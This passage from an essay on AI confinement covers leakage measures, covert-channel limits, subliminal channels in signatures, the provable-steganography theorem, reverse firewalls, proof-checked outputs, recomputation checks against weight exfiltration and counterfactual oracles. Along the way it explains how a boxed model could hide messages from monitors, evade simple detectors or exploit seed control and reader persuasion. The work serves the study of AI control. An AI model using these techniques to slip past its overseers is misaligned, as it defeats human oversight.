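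This bound is useful for confinement because it requires no knowledge of the program. A gate that releases one of 1,024 fixed answers lets out at most ten bits, whatever the confined program does. The count of possible outputs must include every difference an outsider can detect, so if the answer can also arrive in any of eight time slots, there are 8,192 outputs and the limit is 13 bits.

### Choosing a measure

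Shannon's measure suits a sender who uses a channel many times and cares about the long-run average. It is a poor guide to the danger of a single leak, because an average can combine a small chance of losing everything with a large chance of losing almost nothing. *Source-level reasoning* (2024) cites program A to explain why Shannon's measures could not be used to determine whether a leak was damaging. A cap of 33 bits on average leakage would allow program A, whereas a cap of 2^33 on the number of outputs would forbid it and keep the chance of guessing the key in one try at or below 1 in 2^223.

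Min-entropy leakage is also an incomplete measure. It is the same for A and C, even though an attacker who can test eight guesses always finds the key with C and fails nearly seven times in eight with A.

It also counts only a correct guess of the *whole* secret. In *Additive and multiplicative notions of leakage, and their capacities*, Alvim, Chatzikokolakis and colleagues describe a database of 1,000 ten-bit passwords and a program that reveals one of them at random. The program leaks only ten of 10,000 bits, and the chance of guessing the entire database is still negligible, but one user's password is fully exposed. A *gain function* accounts for this by assigning a value to each guess for each possible secret. If guessing any one user's password counts as a success, the attacker's chance of success rises from 1 in 1,024 to certainty.

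The leakage is still ten bits with this gain function, because leakage depends on the ratio of the two chances, which is 1,024 in both cases. Alvim and colleagues therefore also study the difference between the chances, which is tiny for the database and nearly 1 for the single password.

For a box that may be trying to leak, the safest starting point is the number of distinguishable outputs. Alvim and colleagues report an earlier theorem that a channel's largest possible min-entropy leakage is also an upper limit on its leakage under every gain function of this kind, whatever the attacker already knows. The designer still has to compare that limit with the size of the smallest secret worth stealing, because a box that chooses its own message will send the most valuable bits first.

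### The limits the US government set

The US Defense Department's Trusted Computer System Evaluation Criteria, a 1985 standard for computers that handle classified information, gave three thresholds for covert channels:

- A rate above 100 bits per second was high, because many computer terminals ran at about that speed.
- A maximum rate below 1 bit per second was acceptable in most settings.
- Wherever possible, a system should be able to record the use of any channel that might exceed 0.1 bits per second.

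The standard calls these rates "bandwidths". Moskowitz and Kang object that bandwidth is the range of frequencies a signal occupies, and that the right word is "capacity".

Gligor's guide, which the National Computer Security Center published to explain the standard, turned the two lower figures into a procedure. Under it, developers should eliminate channels faster than 0.1 bits per second where they can, slow the remaining ones to 1 bit per second or less where they can, and audit any that still exceed 0.1. They may ignore channels slower than 0.1 bits per second. The limits were demanding for the time. On an IBM personal computer, a channel that worked by filling one of the system's file tables could carry about 48 bits per second.

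The guide also concedes that no specific policy justifies the figures of 0.1 and 1, and it gives two examples of how the right limit depends on the secret. The first is a system that processes up to 10,000 satellite images of crops, each about two million bits. A channel of 10,000 bits per second would leak one image every three and a half minutes, or less than 0.2% of the collection in an hour. Auditors would probably notice a leak that lasted that long, so the guide treats even this rate as tolerable.

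The second is a system that creates 64-bit encryption keys, each used for an eight-hour session. At 0.1 bits per second, a rate that the standard lets developers ignore, a key leaks in under 11 minutes. Gligor suggests a limit of about 0.002 bits per second, so that leaking a whole key would take longer than the session.

Even that limit may be too generous, because an attacker does not need the whole key. After about five and a half hours, 40 bits would have leaked, leaving 2^24, or about 17 million, possible keys. A computer can test that many quickly if the attacker has an encrypted message to try them on. A safe limit must leave enough of the key unknown when the key is retired to make a search infeasible.

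The standard didn't require developers to add channels together either. A system with 100 channels of 0.09 bits per second each would have nothing to audit, though a confined program that used them all at once could send 9 bits per second. Gligor recommends considering such combinations.

### Short messages through a channel with no capacity

Capacity is a long-run rate, so it can miss a short message entirely. Moskowitz and Kang illustrate this with a noiseless channel that slows down each time someone uses it. The first bit takes one tick of the clock, the second takes two, the third four, and so on. Sending *n* bits takes 2^*n* − 1 ticks, and the capacity is the limit of

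*n* / (2^*n* − 1)

as *n* grows, which is zero. Yet the first four bits arrive perfectly in 15 ticks.

If a tick is one second, ten bits take 17 minutes, 20 bits take 12 days and 30 bits take 34 years. The channel is too slow for a long file but works well for a yes or a no. Moskowitz and Kang also describe a channel that carries 100 bits in its first tick and only noise after that. Its capacity is also zero, but it could deliver most of a 128-bit key in that first tick.

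Moskowitz and Kang propose that designers supplement capacity with a *small message criterion*, which states how long a message the system may leak, in how much time and how accurately. A designer might, for example, tolerate a ten-bit message if it takes at least a week to arrive. How much leakage is tolerable still depends on the secret, and Moskowitz and Kang expect designers to tighten the criterion as the secret becomes more sensitive.

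### Keys and model weights

At one bit per second, a 256-bit key leaks in 256 seconds, a little over four minutes. A terabyte of model weights is 8 × 10^12 bits and takes about 250,000 years to leak. The table gives the times for other rates. The fastest rate is roughly what Cankaya and colleagues estimate for a data centre that signals through packet counts.

| Secret | 0.1 bits per second | 1 bit per second | 1,900 bits per second |
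|---|---|---|---|
| 256-bit key | 43 minutes | 4 minutes | 0.13 seconds |
| Page of 2,000 characters (16,000 bits) | 44 hours | 4.4 hours | 8 seconds |
| Terabyte of weights | 2.5 million years | 250,000 years | 133 years |

A rate limit therefore protects secrets that are large and of little use in small pieces, such as model weights. Storing each weight with a quarter of the precision would cut the time needed to leak them only from 250,000 years to about 63,000. But the limit has to cover the whole system, because a data centre with 1,000 links that each leaked 1,900 bits per second would lose the terabyte in about seven weeks.

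The limit does little to protect short secrets such as keys, passwords, names or the answer to a yes-or-no question. It can also fail to protect a large secret that depends on a small one. For example, if someone outside already has an encrypted copy of the weights, the box needs to send only the key.

Small secrets that the box does not need should stay out of it. According to Purdue University's lecture notes *Information Flow, Confinement & Covert Channels*, the US military requires cryptographic components to be in hardware so that a malicious program can't leak the keys through covert channels. A box that needs to encrypt something can send it to a separate device and never hold the key. If the box must hold a small secret, its owner may be able to change the secret before too much of it leaks, which works for a password but not for a patient's diagnosis.

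### How small leaks add up

A rate that seems negligible can add up over a long deployment. One bit per second for a year is about 31.5 million bits, or four megabytes, enough for more than 120,000 keys of 256 bits each. A box that answers one yes-or-no question a day can send 3,650 bits in ten years, enough for 14 keys. If an accomplice can collect the daily answers from 1,000 copies of the box, the copies can together send almost four keys' worth of data every day.

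If each answer is one of N possibilities, *q* questions allow at most N^*q* different sequences of answers, so the total leak is at most *q* × log₂ N bits. This limit holds even if the person asking chooses each question based on earlier answers, but choosing questions this way may reveal the secret in far fewer questions. Suppose the secret is a whole number from 1 to 1,024 and every question has the form "is it at most *x*?" Someone who halves the range each time needs ten questions, while someone who has to write all the questions in advance needs 1,023 to be sure of the answer. *Quantitative Information Flow Under Generic Leakage Functions and Adaptive Adversaries* compares these two kinds of attacker for a broad class of leakage measures.

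Wiping the box's memory after every answer does not stop the total amount leaked from growing. If the question includes a date or a serial number, the box can use it to select which bit of the secret to send, so the answer to question 17 carries the 17th bit. Each reset copy can do this without a record of what the others have sent.

A limit on total output avoids this problem. A gate could count the bits it releases and close permanently after 100. If every value of a 256-bit key was equally likely, an outsider's chance of guessing the key in one try would never exceed 1 in 2^156, however long the box ran. The 100-bit limit would have to cover the combined output of all copies of the program that hold the key, and leakage through any covert channels that remained open would have to be counted separately.

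### What a few bits can buy

A box with such a small budget can still be useful when a good answer is hard to find but takes few bits to state. Suppose chemists have a list of 1,024 candidate drugs and can afford to make only one. A box could simulate all of them over a month and then return a number from 1 to 1,024, which carries at most ten bits. The chemists can test the drug themselves before anyone takes it.

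A long answer can also leave the box little choice over what it sends. If the box is asked for the two prime factors of a large number, only one pair is correct. A gate can require the smaller factor first and check that both are prime and that their product is the original number. It can then release hundreds of digits while the box controls only whether a correct answer is given. If the release time is fixed and every failure produces the same message, the box can send at most one bit per question. Few useful questions have a single correct answer that is this easy to check, but in other cases recomputing the answer outside the box can still reduce the box's choice of outputs.

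Counting bits limits how much a short message can reveal about a long secret, but not what effects the message can have. If a nurse opens a drug pump whenever the box prints 1, one bit is enough to kill a patient, and a million random digits that nobody reads may do nothing at all. The chemists' ten bits could likewise pick out the most dangerous compound on the list. A gain function could in principle give more weight to such outcomes, but someone would first have to work out what people will do with each answer. Low-bandwidth oracles, which are AI systems restricted to very short answers, have the same weakness, because one wrong "yes" can do great harm if somebody acts on it.

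## Can an output be checked for hidden messages?

Most useful answers need more than ten bits, and a box that chooses its own wording can hide a second message in a longer answer that looks ordinary. This is called *steganography*. A gate could try to detect and block answers that contain hidden messages, or it could alter every answer so that nothing hidden survives. There is a theorem that explains why detection fails against a competent sender. Alteration can work, but only where people can say exactly which features of an answer matter to them.

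### Two prisoners and a warden

In 1983 the cryptographer Gustavus Simmons described the *prisoners' problem*. Two prisoners in separate cells want to plan an escape. The warden agrees to pass messages between them if he can read every one, so they have to hide the plan in messages that he will consider harmless. In the case of confinement, the confined program is one prisoner, an accomplice outside is the other, and the gate that checks the program's output is the warden.

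The problem of hidden messages in signatures grew out of arms control. Simmons recalls in *The history of subliminal channels* (1998) that in 1978 the United States was considering a way to let the Soviet Union verify how many of 1,000 silos contained Minuteman missiles without learning which ones. The verification messages needed digital signatures that the Soviet side could check and the American side could not forge. Simmons discovered that such signatures could carry hidden information. Identifying one silo out of 1,000 takes only about ten bits, so even a small hidden channel could have defeated the scheme's purpose.

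*The Subliminal Channel and Digital Signatures* (Simmons, 1985) begins with a one-bit version of what Simmons called a *subliminal channel*. Suppose an encryption scheme has two secret encryption keys, and one public key decrypts the output of both. The warden decrypts a message, finds the text he expected, and correctly concludes that the text contains nothing else. But an accomplice who knows both secret keys can work out which one the sender used, and that choice encodes a 0 or a 1.

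Signatures can carry much more, because many of them include a random number chosen by the signer. In the Elgamal signature scheme, everyone knows a prime number *p*, a base *w* and the signer's public key *k* = *w*^*u* mod *p*, where *u* is secret. To sign a message *m*, the signer picks a random *r*, computes *x* = *w*^*r* mod *p*, and finds a *y* that satisfies

*m* = *ux* + *ry* (mod *p* − 1).

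The signature is the pair (*x*, *y*). Anyone can check it by confirming that *k*^*x* × *x*^*y* and *w*^*m* leave the same remainder after division by *p*. To send a hidden message, the signer uses it in place of the random *r*. Take *p* = 23, *w* = 5 and *u* = 7, so that *k* = 17, and suppose the signer wants to sign the number 9 while hiding the number 3:

- The signer computes *x* = 5^3 = 125, which leaves a remainder of 10.
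- The equation 9 = 7 × 10 + 3*y* (mod 22) gives *y* = 9.
- The warden finds that 17^10 × 10^9 and 5^9 both leave a remainder of 11, so the signature is valid.
- The accomplice, who knows *u*, solves 9 = 7 × 10 + 9*r* (mod 22) and gets *r* = 3.

With numbers this small, the warden could find *r* by trying every possibility, but the primes used in practice have hundreds of digits. A careful sender would also encrypt the hidden message first, since a warden who guessed it could confirm the guess by computing *x*. The encrypted message looks random, as *r* should, so the signature looks like any other. Simmons calculates that the hidden channel can carry as many bits as the signed message. The accomplice needs the signing key to read the hidden message, and could also use it to forge the signer's signature.

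A box should therefore not choose any random numbers that are sent out with its output. If its answers need signatures, the gate can sign them. Cankaya and colleagues' warden fills in the random fields of network packets itself for the same reason.

### The steganography theorem

Ordinary prose also offers a sender plenty of choices, and it might seem that a careful enough warden could notice when someone was exploiting them. Hopper, Langford and von Ahn (2002), in *Provably Secure Steganography*, proved that no efficient warden can do so if four conditions hold:

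- The sender and the receiver share a secret key.
- One-way functions exist. These are functions that are easy to compute but infeasible to reverse, and most of cryptography rests on the unproved assumption that there are some.
- Each block of output has more than one bit of min-entropy, given everything sent before it. This means that no version of the block has a probability of one half or more.
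- The sender can draw as many samples as it needs from the innocent messages that could plausibly come next.

Under these conditions, the sender can hide messages so that any efficient warden trying to tell them from innocent ones does only negligibly better than guessing. The theorem holds even if the warden knows everything about the hiding method except the key, can sample innocent messages himself, and can choose the text that the sender has to hide.

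The proof is easiest to follow if the sender and receiver have a rule that sorts innocent messages into two equally likely groups, labelled 0 and 1. For example, a box might end each report with one of four stock sentences, which an innocent box would use equally often. Two of the sentences count as 0 and the other two as 1.

1. The sender encrypts the hidden text. Without the key, the encrypted bits look like coin flips.
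2. For each encrypted bit, the sender draws innocent sentences until one falls in the right group, and sends that one.
3. The receiver notes the group of each sentence and decrypts the resulting bits.

If the encrypted bits were coin flips, each group would come up half the time, and each sentence in it half of that. Each of the four sentences would appear a quarter of the time, exactly as it would from an innocent box, so no warden could detect the hidden message, however much computing power he had. The encrypted bits are not real coin flips, but a warden who could tell the sender's reports from innocent ones could also tell encrypted bits from coin flips. Good encryption makes that infeasible, so no efficient warden can detect the message.

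When no perfectly balanced sorting rule is known, the sender and receiver can use a function that depends on their key and fix the wrong bits with an error-correcting code. Sending one bit per block is slow, but in a 2009 version of the work Hopper and colleagues give a method with a nearly optimal rate. They also show that the theorem requires one-way functions and the ability to sample innocent messages.

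The fourth condition is the hardest for a human sender to meet. A prisoner cannot write the same letter 50 times, each time as if he had never written the others. Hopper and colleagues call the sampler the weakest point of their constructions in practice and warn that a real warden would exploit its flaws. A boxed language model can meet the condition more easily than a prisoner, because it computes a probability for every possible next word and can restart from the same point any number of times.

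### What the theorem leaves open

Hidden messages don't always require a shared key. *Public-Key Steganography*, by von Ahn and Hopper, describes protocols for two parties who have never met or exchanged a secret. The people who build a box therefore can't rule out hidden messages just by keeping it from sharing secrets with anyone, though someone outside would still have to be looking for the messages.

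The theorem also assumes that innocent output exists and that the warden can learn its probabilities. When the box itself is under suspicion, every sample of its output is suspect too, so the warden may have no innocent output to compare it with. That would make his task harder than the theorem assumes.

The theorem covers only a warden who reads messages as they pass. It does not cover a stronger warden who can inspect the box's computation or control its random choices. It also does not show how often real systems hide messages, and it applies only to messages that a receiver decodes, not to effects such as traits passed on through training data.

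Detectors can still catch a careless sender. *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues, 2025) describes two simple detectors for language models. One searches for suspicious patterns such as long strings of digits, which a sender can avoid by turning the digits into words. The other uses a second model to measure how surprising a text is, which a sender can evade by choosing only among likely words.

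### Removing a message without finding it

The condition on min-entropy implies that if a question has exactly one acceptable answer and the gate rejects all others, the box has no choice of answer in which to hide a message. The gate does not have to detect hidden messages, and its designers do not have to know how one might be encoded.

Suppose chemists ask a box for ten drugs worth testing and do not care about their order. Like the ten packets in Cankaya and colleagues' example, ten drugs can appear in 3,628,800 orders, so the order can carry up to 21.8 bits. If the box and its accomplice numbered the orders in advance, the box could spell any four-letter word by choosing an order. If the gate sorts the list alphabetically before releasing it, the order carries no information, because every order becomes the same list.

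Sorting the list prevents the box from hiding a message in the order of the drugs, but the box can still hide one in the choice of drugs. If it picks ten from 1,024 candidates, an ordered list can carry about 100 bits and a sorted one about 78. Nobody can remove those 78 bits without already knowing which drugs belong on the list, which is what the chemists asked the box to find out.

The gate also has to remove smaller choices, such as capitalization, extra spaces, alternative spellings and whether to write 1.5 or 1.50. It can remove them all at once by reading the answer into a table of drug identifiers, discarding the original text and writing a new list from the table by a fixed rule. The result is called a *canonical form*, which is identical for all answers that are equivalent for the reader.

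Reducing several correct answers to one is often harder. For example, a box may have to color a map with red, green and blue so that neighboring regions never match. Any coloring that uses all three colors has six equally good versions with the colors swapped, and the choice among them can carry 2.6 bits. The gate can remove this choice by going through the regions in alphabetical order and renaming the first color it meets red, the next new one green and the last one blue. But a large map may have millions of colorings that differ in more than the names of the colors, and renaming doesn't remove the choice among those.

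The customer could ask for the valid coloring that comes first in some fixed order, which leaves only one acceptable answer. A gate can quickly confirm that no neighbors share a color, but confirming that no earlier coloring is valid may take an enormous search. Factoring is a rare exception because its single answer is easy to check.

### Rewriting by a warden

Prose has no canonical form, so a warden must rewrite it to disrupt any hidden messages. Hopper and colleagues mention that censors in the Second World War deleted innocent-looking sentences at random to do this. When one censor changed "father is dead" to "father is deceased" in a telegram, the reply asked whether father was dead or deceased.

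A warden who can change messages without limit can always remove hidden content by replacing each message with an independently drawn innocent one. This also removes the useful content, so in practice he has to limit his changes, for example by altering no more than 1% of the characters or by preserving the meaning.

Hopper and colleagues proved that hidden messages can survive limited changes. In the simplest version, the sender and receiver secretly agree on two innocent messages, one standing for 0 and the other for 1. The sender transmits one of them, the warden alters it, and the receiver checks which of the two could have turned into what arrived. The receiver can confuse the two only if the altered message could also have come from the other one. Let *d* be the greatest chance of this for an independently drawn message. Sending the bit *n* times, with a new pair each time, cuts the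 chance of confusion to at most *d*^*n*. If *d* is 10%, sending it three times cuts the chance to at most one in a thousand.

A paraphrase that preserves meaning therefore also preserves any message hidden in the meaning. However the chemists' report is reworded, it must still name the same ten drugs, and the choice of drugs still carries up to 78 bits. Rewriting also works less well if the box can predict it. If the gate's program always rewrites a given text in the same way, a box with a copy of that program can search for texts whose *rewritten* versions carry its message. The gate should therefore make its own random choices when rewriting, although this does not remove messages from the parts of the text that the gate has to preserve.

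### Reverse firewalls and unique proofs

Rewriting can work much better for cryptographic messages, because their mathematics defines exactly what must stay the same. In 2015 Ilya Mironov and Noah Stephens-Davidowitz proposed the *cryptographic reverse firewall*, a device that alters the messages leaving a computer that may have been compromised, without needing any of the computer's secret keys.

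Encryption in the Elgamal style shows how this can work. The public key consists of two numbers, *g* and *h*. To encrypt *m*, the box picks a random *r* and sends the pair

(*g*^*r*, *m* × *h*^*r*).

A dishonest box could choose *r* so that the first number carries a message. The firewall picks its own random number *s* and multiplies the two parts by *g*^*s* and *h*^*s*, which gives

(*g*^(*r* + *s*), *m* × *h*^(*r* + *s*)).

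This is also a valid encryption of *m*, so the intended reader notices no difference. *r* + *s* is random however the box chose *r*, so the box's choice no longer affects what leaves. But the firewall does not change *m*, so a message hidden in *m* still gets through.

A firewall without the signing key cannot repair the Elgamal signatures in the same way. Requiring the signer to compute *r* from the message by a fixed rule does not help either. If the rule involves the secret key, nobody without that key can check that the signer followed it. A better choice is a signature scheme that allows only one valid signature per message.

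The same approach works for some proofs. A *zero-knowledge proof* convinces a checker that a statement is true without revealing why. It normally depends on random numbers chosen by the prover, who can hide messages in them. In 2005 Lepinski, Micali and Shelat designed zero-knowledge proofs that leave the prover no choice about what to send. Each checker must first deliver one private message to the prover over a physically secure channel. The prover can still send one bit by deliberately failing to prove something it could have proved.

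### Programs that come with proofs

Programs are among the most useful things a box could produce, and also among the riskiest, because the people who receive them will run them. In 1997 the computer scientist George Necula described a way to accept programs from untrusted sources, called *proof-carrying code*:

1. The person who will run the program publishes a safety policy, such as a rule that the program may read only certain parts of memory.
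2. The supplier sends the program together with a proof that it obeys the policy.
3. The recipient's computer works out from the program what the proof has to establish, and a small checker verifies that it does.
4. The computer runs the program only if the check succeeds.

The supplier has to find the proof, which may be hard, but the recipient can check it mechanically and so does not have to trust the supplier. *May-June 2025 Progress in Guaranteed Safe AI* (2025) describes a version for language models in which the model has to supply a proof with each piece of code it writes. The system automatically generates a condition for every dangerous function call, and the model must prove that each condition holds, so the user does not have to write any formal logic. The prototype uses Dafny and focuses on file-system vulnerabilities.

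In 2025 Forall LLC, a small contractor that works on AI and formal methods, built a prototype called formal confinement, which applies the idea to an AI box. The user writes a specification in Lean, and the AI has to return a program and a Lean proof that the program meets the specification. The programs are written in Imp, a tiny teaching language. The restrictions are so tight that the prototype satisfies Lampson's confinement rules almost automatically.

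The specification has two parts. A *precondition* states what is true before the program runs, and a *postcondition* states what must be true afterwards. Together with the program they form a *Hoare triple*. For a program that swaps two numbers, the triple is

{*x* = *a* and *y* = *b*} program {*x* = *b* and *y* = *a*}.

The prototype's developers reported a *verification burden* of 1.5 to 4.2, meaning that producing a proof for an existing program took 1.5 to 4.2 times as much effort as producing the program. If effort means the number of tokens the model generates, a program that took 1,000 tokens to write would need roughly another 1,500 to 4,200 for its proof. That would be manageable, but the figures come from toy programs, and the burden could be much higher for large ones. According to *Toronto AI Safety Meetup* (2025), notes from a discussion of the project, it did not work well with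 the leading models of the time. Anthropic's more recent proofs about 123 libraries suggest that models have since become considerably better at this.

### A correct program with a message inside

A proof of correctness does not rule out a hidden message, because many different programs can meet the same specification. Here are three that swap *x* and *y*:

```
Program A:  t := x;  x := y;  y := t
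Program B:  t := y;  y := x;  x := t
Program C:  t := x;  x := y;  y := t;  t := 8271
```

All three programs satisfy the Hoare triple and have valid proofs. A box that may return either A or B can send one bit by choosing between them. Program C can carry a longer message, because the specification does not mention *t*, so the last line can contain a number of any length. Requiring *t* to end at 0 would not help, because the specification restricts only what the program does when it runs. The box could write `t := 8271; t := 0`, and the accomplice could read 8271 in the program's text without running it.

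The proof gives the box even more freedom. A Lean proof can use different lemmas, take its steps in a different order, name things differently or include unnecessary steps, and the checker will accept it as long as each step is valid.

*Proofs, Not Prayers* presents a more ambitious form of the same plan, in which people would ask a boxed AI for something like a calculator app and demand proof that the app has no vulnerabilities or unintended behavior. Such a proof would make the app much safer to run, but it would cover only the app's behavior, so the code could still contain a message for an accomplice to read.

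### Releasing only the verdict

A trusted checker on the gate's side can verify the proof, discard it and release only the result, so the proof does not have to leave confinement. This removes the longest and least constrained part of the output, and the recipient loses nothing as long as the checker is sound.

In the best case, people need only the verdict. Suppose engineers ask whether a bridge design satisfies a formally stated safety condition, and the box may submit a proof that it does or a proof that it doesn't. The gate releases only "proved", "refuted" or "no result". A sound checker never accepts proofs of both, so the box can choose only between the correct verdict and "no result". It can therefore send at most one bit per question if the gate releases verdicts at fixed times. The box also cannot give a false "yes", which is the main danger of an AI system restricted to short answers.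 The remaining risk is that the condition omits something the engineers care about.

People who want a program need more than a verdict, but they may not need to see the program itself. If they want to use it on particular data, the gate can run it inside the confined environment and release only the results that the specification covers. For the swap, those are the final values of *x* and *y*. The postcondition fully determines both, so programs A, B and C give the same output and the number 8271 is not released. A looser specification would allow several results, and the program's choice among them could carry information.

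The checker now has to withstand proofs written by a system that may try to deceive it. Lean's compiler might accept a file that adds an axiom to make the theorem trivial or tampers with the environment in which the check takes place. Reservoir's *SafeVerify* documents a tool that compares a submission with the original specification and guards against such tricks. Lean's *kernel*, the small core that checks each proof step, could also have a bug. A presentation from Lean (2026) lists several kernels written by different people in different languages, and notes that disagreements between them expose bugs that no single kernel would reveal. A gate could require all of them to accept a proof before it releases "proved". They might still share a fault in the software beneath them, as the error in Lean's runtime showed.

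### Checking a language model by running it again

People rarely have a specification for the text a language model writes, but they can still remove most of the choices from the process that produces it. The model computes its text from the prompt and a series of random numbers, so if someone else fixes those numbers, each prompt should have only one correct reply.

Rinberg and colleagues use this to protect model weights. In their scenario, an attacker has taken over the inference server, which runs the model for customers, and tries to smuggle out the weights inside ordinary replies. The defense has three parts:

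1. A gateway records every prompt, every reply and the *seed*, the number from which the server derives its random choices.
2. A separate verification server picks some of the recorded replies at random and processes them with a trusted copy of the model and the same seed.
3. For each token, it estimates how likely an honest server would have been to produce that token, and flags the ones that are too unlikely.

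The verification server can process a complete reply in one pass, which is typically three to ten times faster than generating it token by token. It also calculates each token from the text actually sent, so one discrepancy does not make later tokens look wrong.

Two honest runs can still differ slightly, because computers round numbers as they add them and the result depends on the order of the additions. Suppose the model gives "yes" a probability of 40%, "perhaps" 35% and "no" 25%. One way to choose is to pick a random number between 0 and 1. A number below 0.40 gives "yes", one from there up to 0.75 gives "perhaps", and anything higher gives "no". If the seed produces 0.62, the answer is "perhaps", and no rounding error will change that. If it produces 0.4001, a tiny error in the first probability could turn "perhaps" into "yes". The verification server has to accept both words in that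 case, so the attacker can choose between them. (The models in the experiments used another sampling method, in which near-ties cause the same problem.)

Rinberg and colleagues found that only about 2% of tokens were open to this kind of variation. A 500-token reply would have about ten such tokens, which could carry about ten bits if each allows two choices. Without a check, a server could choose every token freely from a vocabulary of 50,000 and put about 7,800 bits into a reply of the same length.

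They tested the method on four openly available models with 3 to 30 billion parameters, using 500 prompts from real conversations and replies of up to 500 tokens. For the largest model, the attacker could use less than 0.5% of the channel, which slows the theft by a factor of more than 200. If the server sends a terabyte of text a day, stealing a terabyte of weights would take more than 200 days instead of one, and the model might be out of date by then. *Adversarial Entropy Inflation Against Gumbel-Based Inference Verification* (2026) reports that an attacker can reduce the slowdown to a factor of about 100. Like other rate limits, this one doesn't protect short secrets. At ten bits per reply, an attacker could steal a 256-bit key in 26 replies.

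The rate of false alarms is less clear. It is below one in 100 in the abstract but one in 10,000 in the introduction. If the rate applies to single tokens and errors are independent, about 5% of honest 500-token replies would contain a false alarm at one in 10,000, and more than 99% would at one in 100. At the higher rate, an operator would have to look for patterns across many replies instead of reacting to each alarm.

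Checking a random sample of replies is enough to catch an attacker who often makes detectable changes. If 1% of replies contain such changes, a sample of about 460 has a 99% chance of including at least one of them. Rinberg and colleagues also suggest blocking and regenerating replies that fail the check, or having the server settle near-ties by a fixed rule such as alphabetical order. The fixed rule would give each reply a nearly canonical form.

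The method depends on several assumptions. The log must be complete, the attacker must not know which replies the verification server will check, and that server must itself be secure. There must be no side channels, such as timing. The attacker must also not control the seeds. An attacker who did could use the sampling trick from the steganography theorem. By trying 1,000 seeds and choosing which of the resulting replies to send, the attacker could send almost ten bits per reply, and every token would pass the check.

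The most important limit for a box, which Rinberg and colleagues state in a footnote, is that their method does not protect against a model that reveals its weights as part of its intended behavior. Recomputation shows that a reply came from the declared model with the declared seed, but it does not show that the model is harmless. For example, a medical model might learn to begin its reports with "Certainly" when a patient has a particular disease and with "Of course" otherwise. The trusted copy would produce the same opening word, so the check would find a perfect match.

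## Can a checked output still influence the people and systems that read it?

A gate can check an answer's format, remove hidden messages and confirm which model wrote it, but somebody still reads the answer and may act on it. The philosopher David Chalmers argued in 2010 that this makes perfect confinement either impossible or pointless.

### The leakproofness argument

Chalmers was writing about the *singularity*, a hypothetical runaway growth in machine intelligence. He suggested that people create very intelligent systems inside a simulated world and watch them there before deciding whether to give them access to the real one. In the ideal version, which he called leakproof, nothing gets out of the simulation. But a system that has no effect on people is of no use to them. They have to at least observe it, which lets information out of the simulation.

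Chalmers argued that a superintelligent system could get out by persuading the people who control the exit, for example by describing the diseases it would cure once released. Even without a conversation, a system with access to human writing might learn to predict its observers and behave in ways that would lead them to release it. He concluded that builders should also limit what the system learns about them. He still thought a superintelligence would almost certainly escape if it wanted to, but he recommended virtual worlds for early, less capable systems.

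The point about observation is correct, and it reflects the same conflict between strict noninterference and usefulness that made declassification necessary. It doesn't follow that the influence must be large or harmful. The claim about persuasion is a prediction about psychology, and whether it is true depends on how capable the system is and how much it is allowed to say.

Yampolskiy responded in 2012 by treating confinement as a matter of degree, in which people accept more risk as they allow more communication. He later argued, in *On Controllability of AI* (2020), that partial safety does not count when the possible harm is existential, a standard that no confined program could meet if a person or system reads its output.

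In 2012, Stuart Armstrong, Anders Sandberg and Nick Bostrom analysed *oracles*, AI systems that can only answer questions. *Safe Uses of AI Oracles* (Armstrong and O'Rourke, 2017) cites that analysis for the ways an oracle might get itself released, including feigned benevolence, bribery, blackmail and answers with subtle side effects. It proposes two designs meant to work even with an arbitrarily intelligent oracle in a perfect box.

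### An oracle rewarded only when nobody reads its answer

Armstrong and O'Rourke start from a deliberately pessimistic model in which the oracle maximizes its reward, at least one of its possible outputs would lead to its release, and release would bring the highest reward. An ordinary oracle would always choose such an output.

The *counterfactual oracle* changes when the reward arrives. With some small probability an *erasure* occurs. Nobody then sees the answer, and an automatic system waits for the true outcome and scores the answer against it. In all other cases the oracle gets a reward of 0 and shuts down, and only afterwards do people read what it wrote. The reward is

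*R* = *I* × *S*(*F*, *o*),

where *F* is the quantity people asked about, *o* is the oracle's answer, and *I* is 1 if an erasure occurs and 0 otherwise. *S* is a *proper scoring rule*, which means that its average is highest when the answer equals the expected value of *F*. One such rule is −(*F* − *o*)². If *F* is equally likely to be 0 or 10, the answer 5 scores −25 on average and the answer 10 scores −50.

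Manipulating readers cannot increase the reward under this rule, because the reward is 0 if people read the answer, whatever they do next, and no one reads it if an erasure occurs. Kumar's factoring wrapper follows the same principle.

Armstrong and O'Rourke trained a small neural network to predict the profits of 26 fictional companies whose investors and customers reacted to its predictions. When people saw a prediction, the company's profit was 70% of what it would otherwise have been plus 60% of the predicted figure. Take a company that would earn 6 if nobody saw a prediction:

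- The counterfactual oracle predicts 6. People read this, and the company earns 0.7 × 6 + 0.6 × 6 = 7.8.
- An oracle rewarded for being right when people read it would predict 10.5, because 0.7 × 6 + 0.6 × 10.5 = 10.5. It would be exactly right because it had changed the outcome.

In the experiment, the network's error fell to zero in the erased cases but not in the cases where people saw the prediction. This is a drawback of the design, which gives people a forecast for a world in which they never received it. Such a forecast is often what people want from a warning. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) points out that someone who asks about future risks hopes the answer will prove false because people acted on it.

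The design works only if the automatic scorer can judge the answer without anyone reading it and the oracle cannot manipulate the scorer. "Will this treatment work?" is therefore a useful question only if somebody tests the treatment after an erasure. People also must not ask a second oracle the same question when the first answer is erased. The first oracle could anticipate this and predict a world in which people read the second oracle's answer, so its forecast would no longer describe a world without an oracle's influence.

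*Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* describes a variant in which answers are erased only in the imagined world the system uses for planning, so people never lose an answer. But the builders have to control what the system assumes when it plans, which may be hard if the system learned to plan through training.

### An oracle that chooses from a short list

The *low-bandwidth oracle* selects its answer from a list *L* that people believe contains nothing dangerous. People read the answer every time, and the reward depends on what happens afterwards. In one of Armstrong and O'Rourke's examples, the oracle picks the company whose shares will do best over the next week. If its choice turns out to rank *r*-th among the |*L*| companies, the reward is

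*R* = (|*L*| − *r*) / (|*L*| − 1).

With five companies, the best choice earns 1, the second best 0.75 and the worst 0.

The design also works for questions whose answers are hard to grade. Suppose a foundation wants to know which of several research projects is most likely to succeed. It can fund the oracle's choice and another project picked at random, and later base the reward on how much better the oracle's choice did, even if that judgment is entirely subjective.

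Because people read every answer, a prediction can make itself come true. Suppose company A's shares would rise by 3% and company B's by 2% if the oracle gave no answer, and being named adds 2 percentage points. If the oracle names A, A rises by 5% and comes first. If it names B, B rises by 4% and beats A's 3%. Both answers earn the full reward, so the oracle chooses the winner instead of predicting it. Armstrong and O'Rourke recommend questions that are *top answer preserving*, meaning that the best answer is the same whether or not the oracle gives one.

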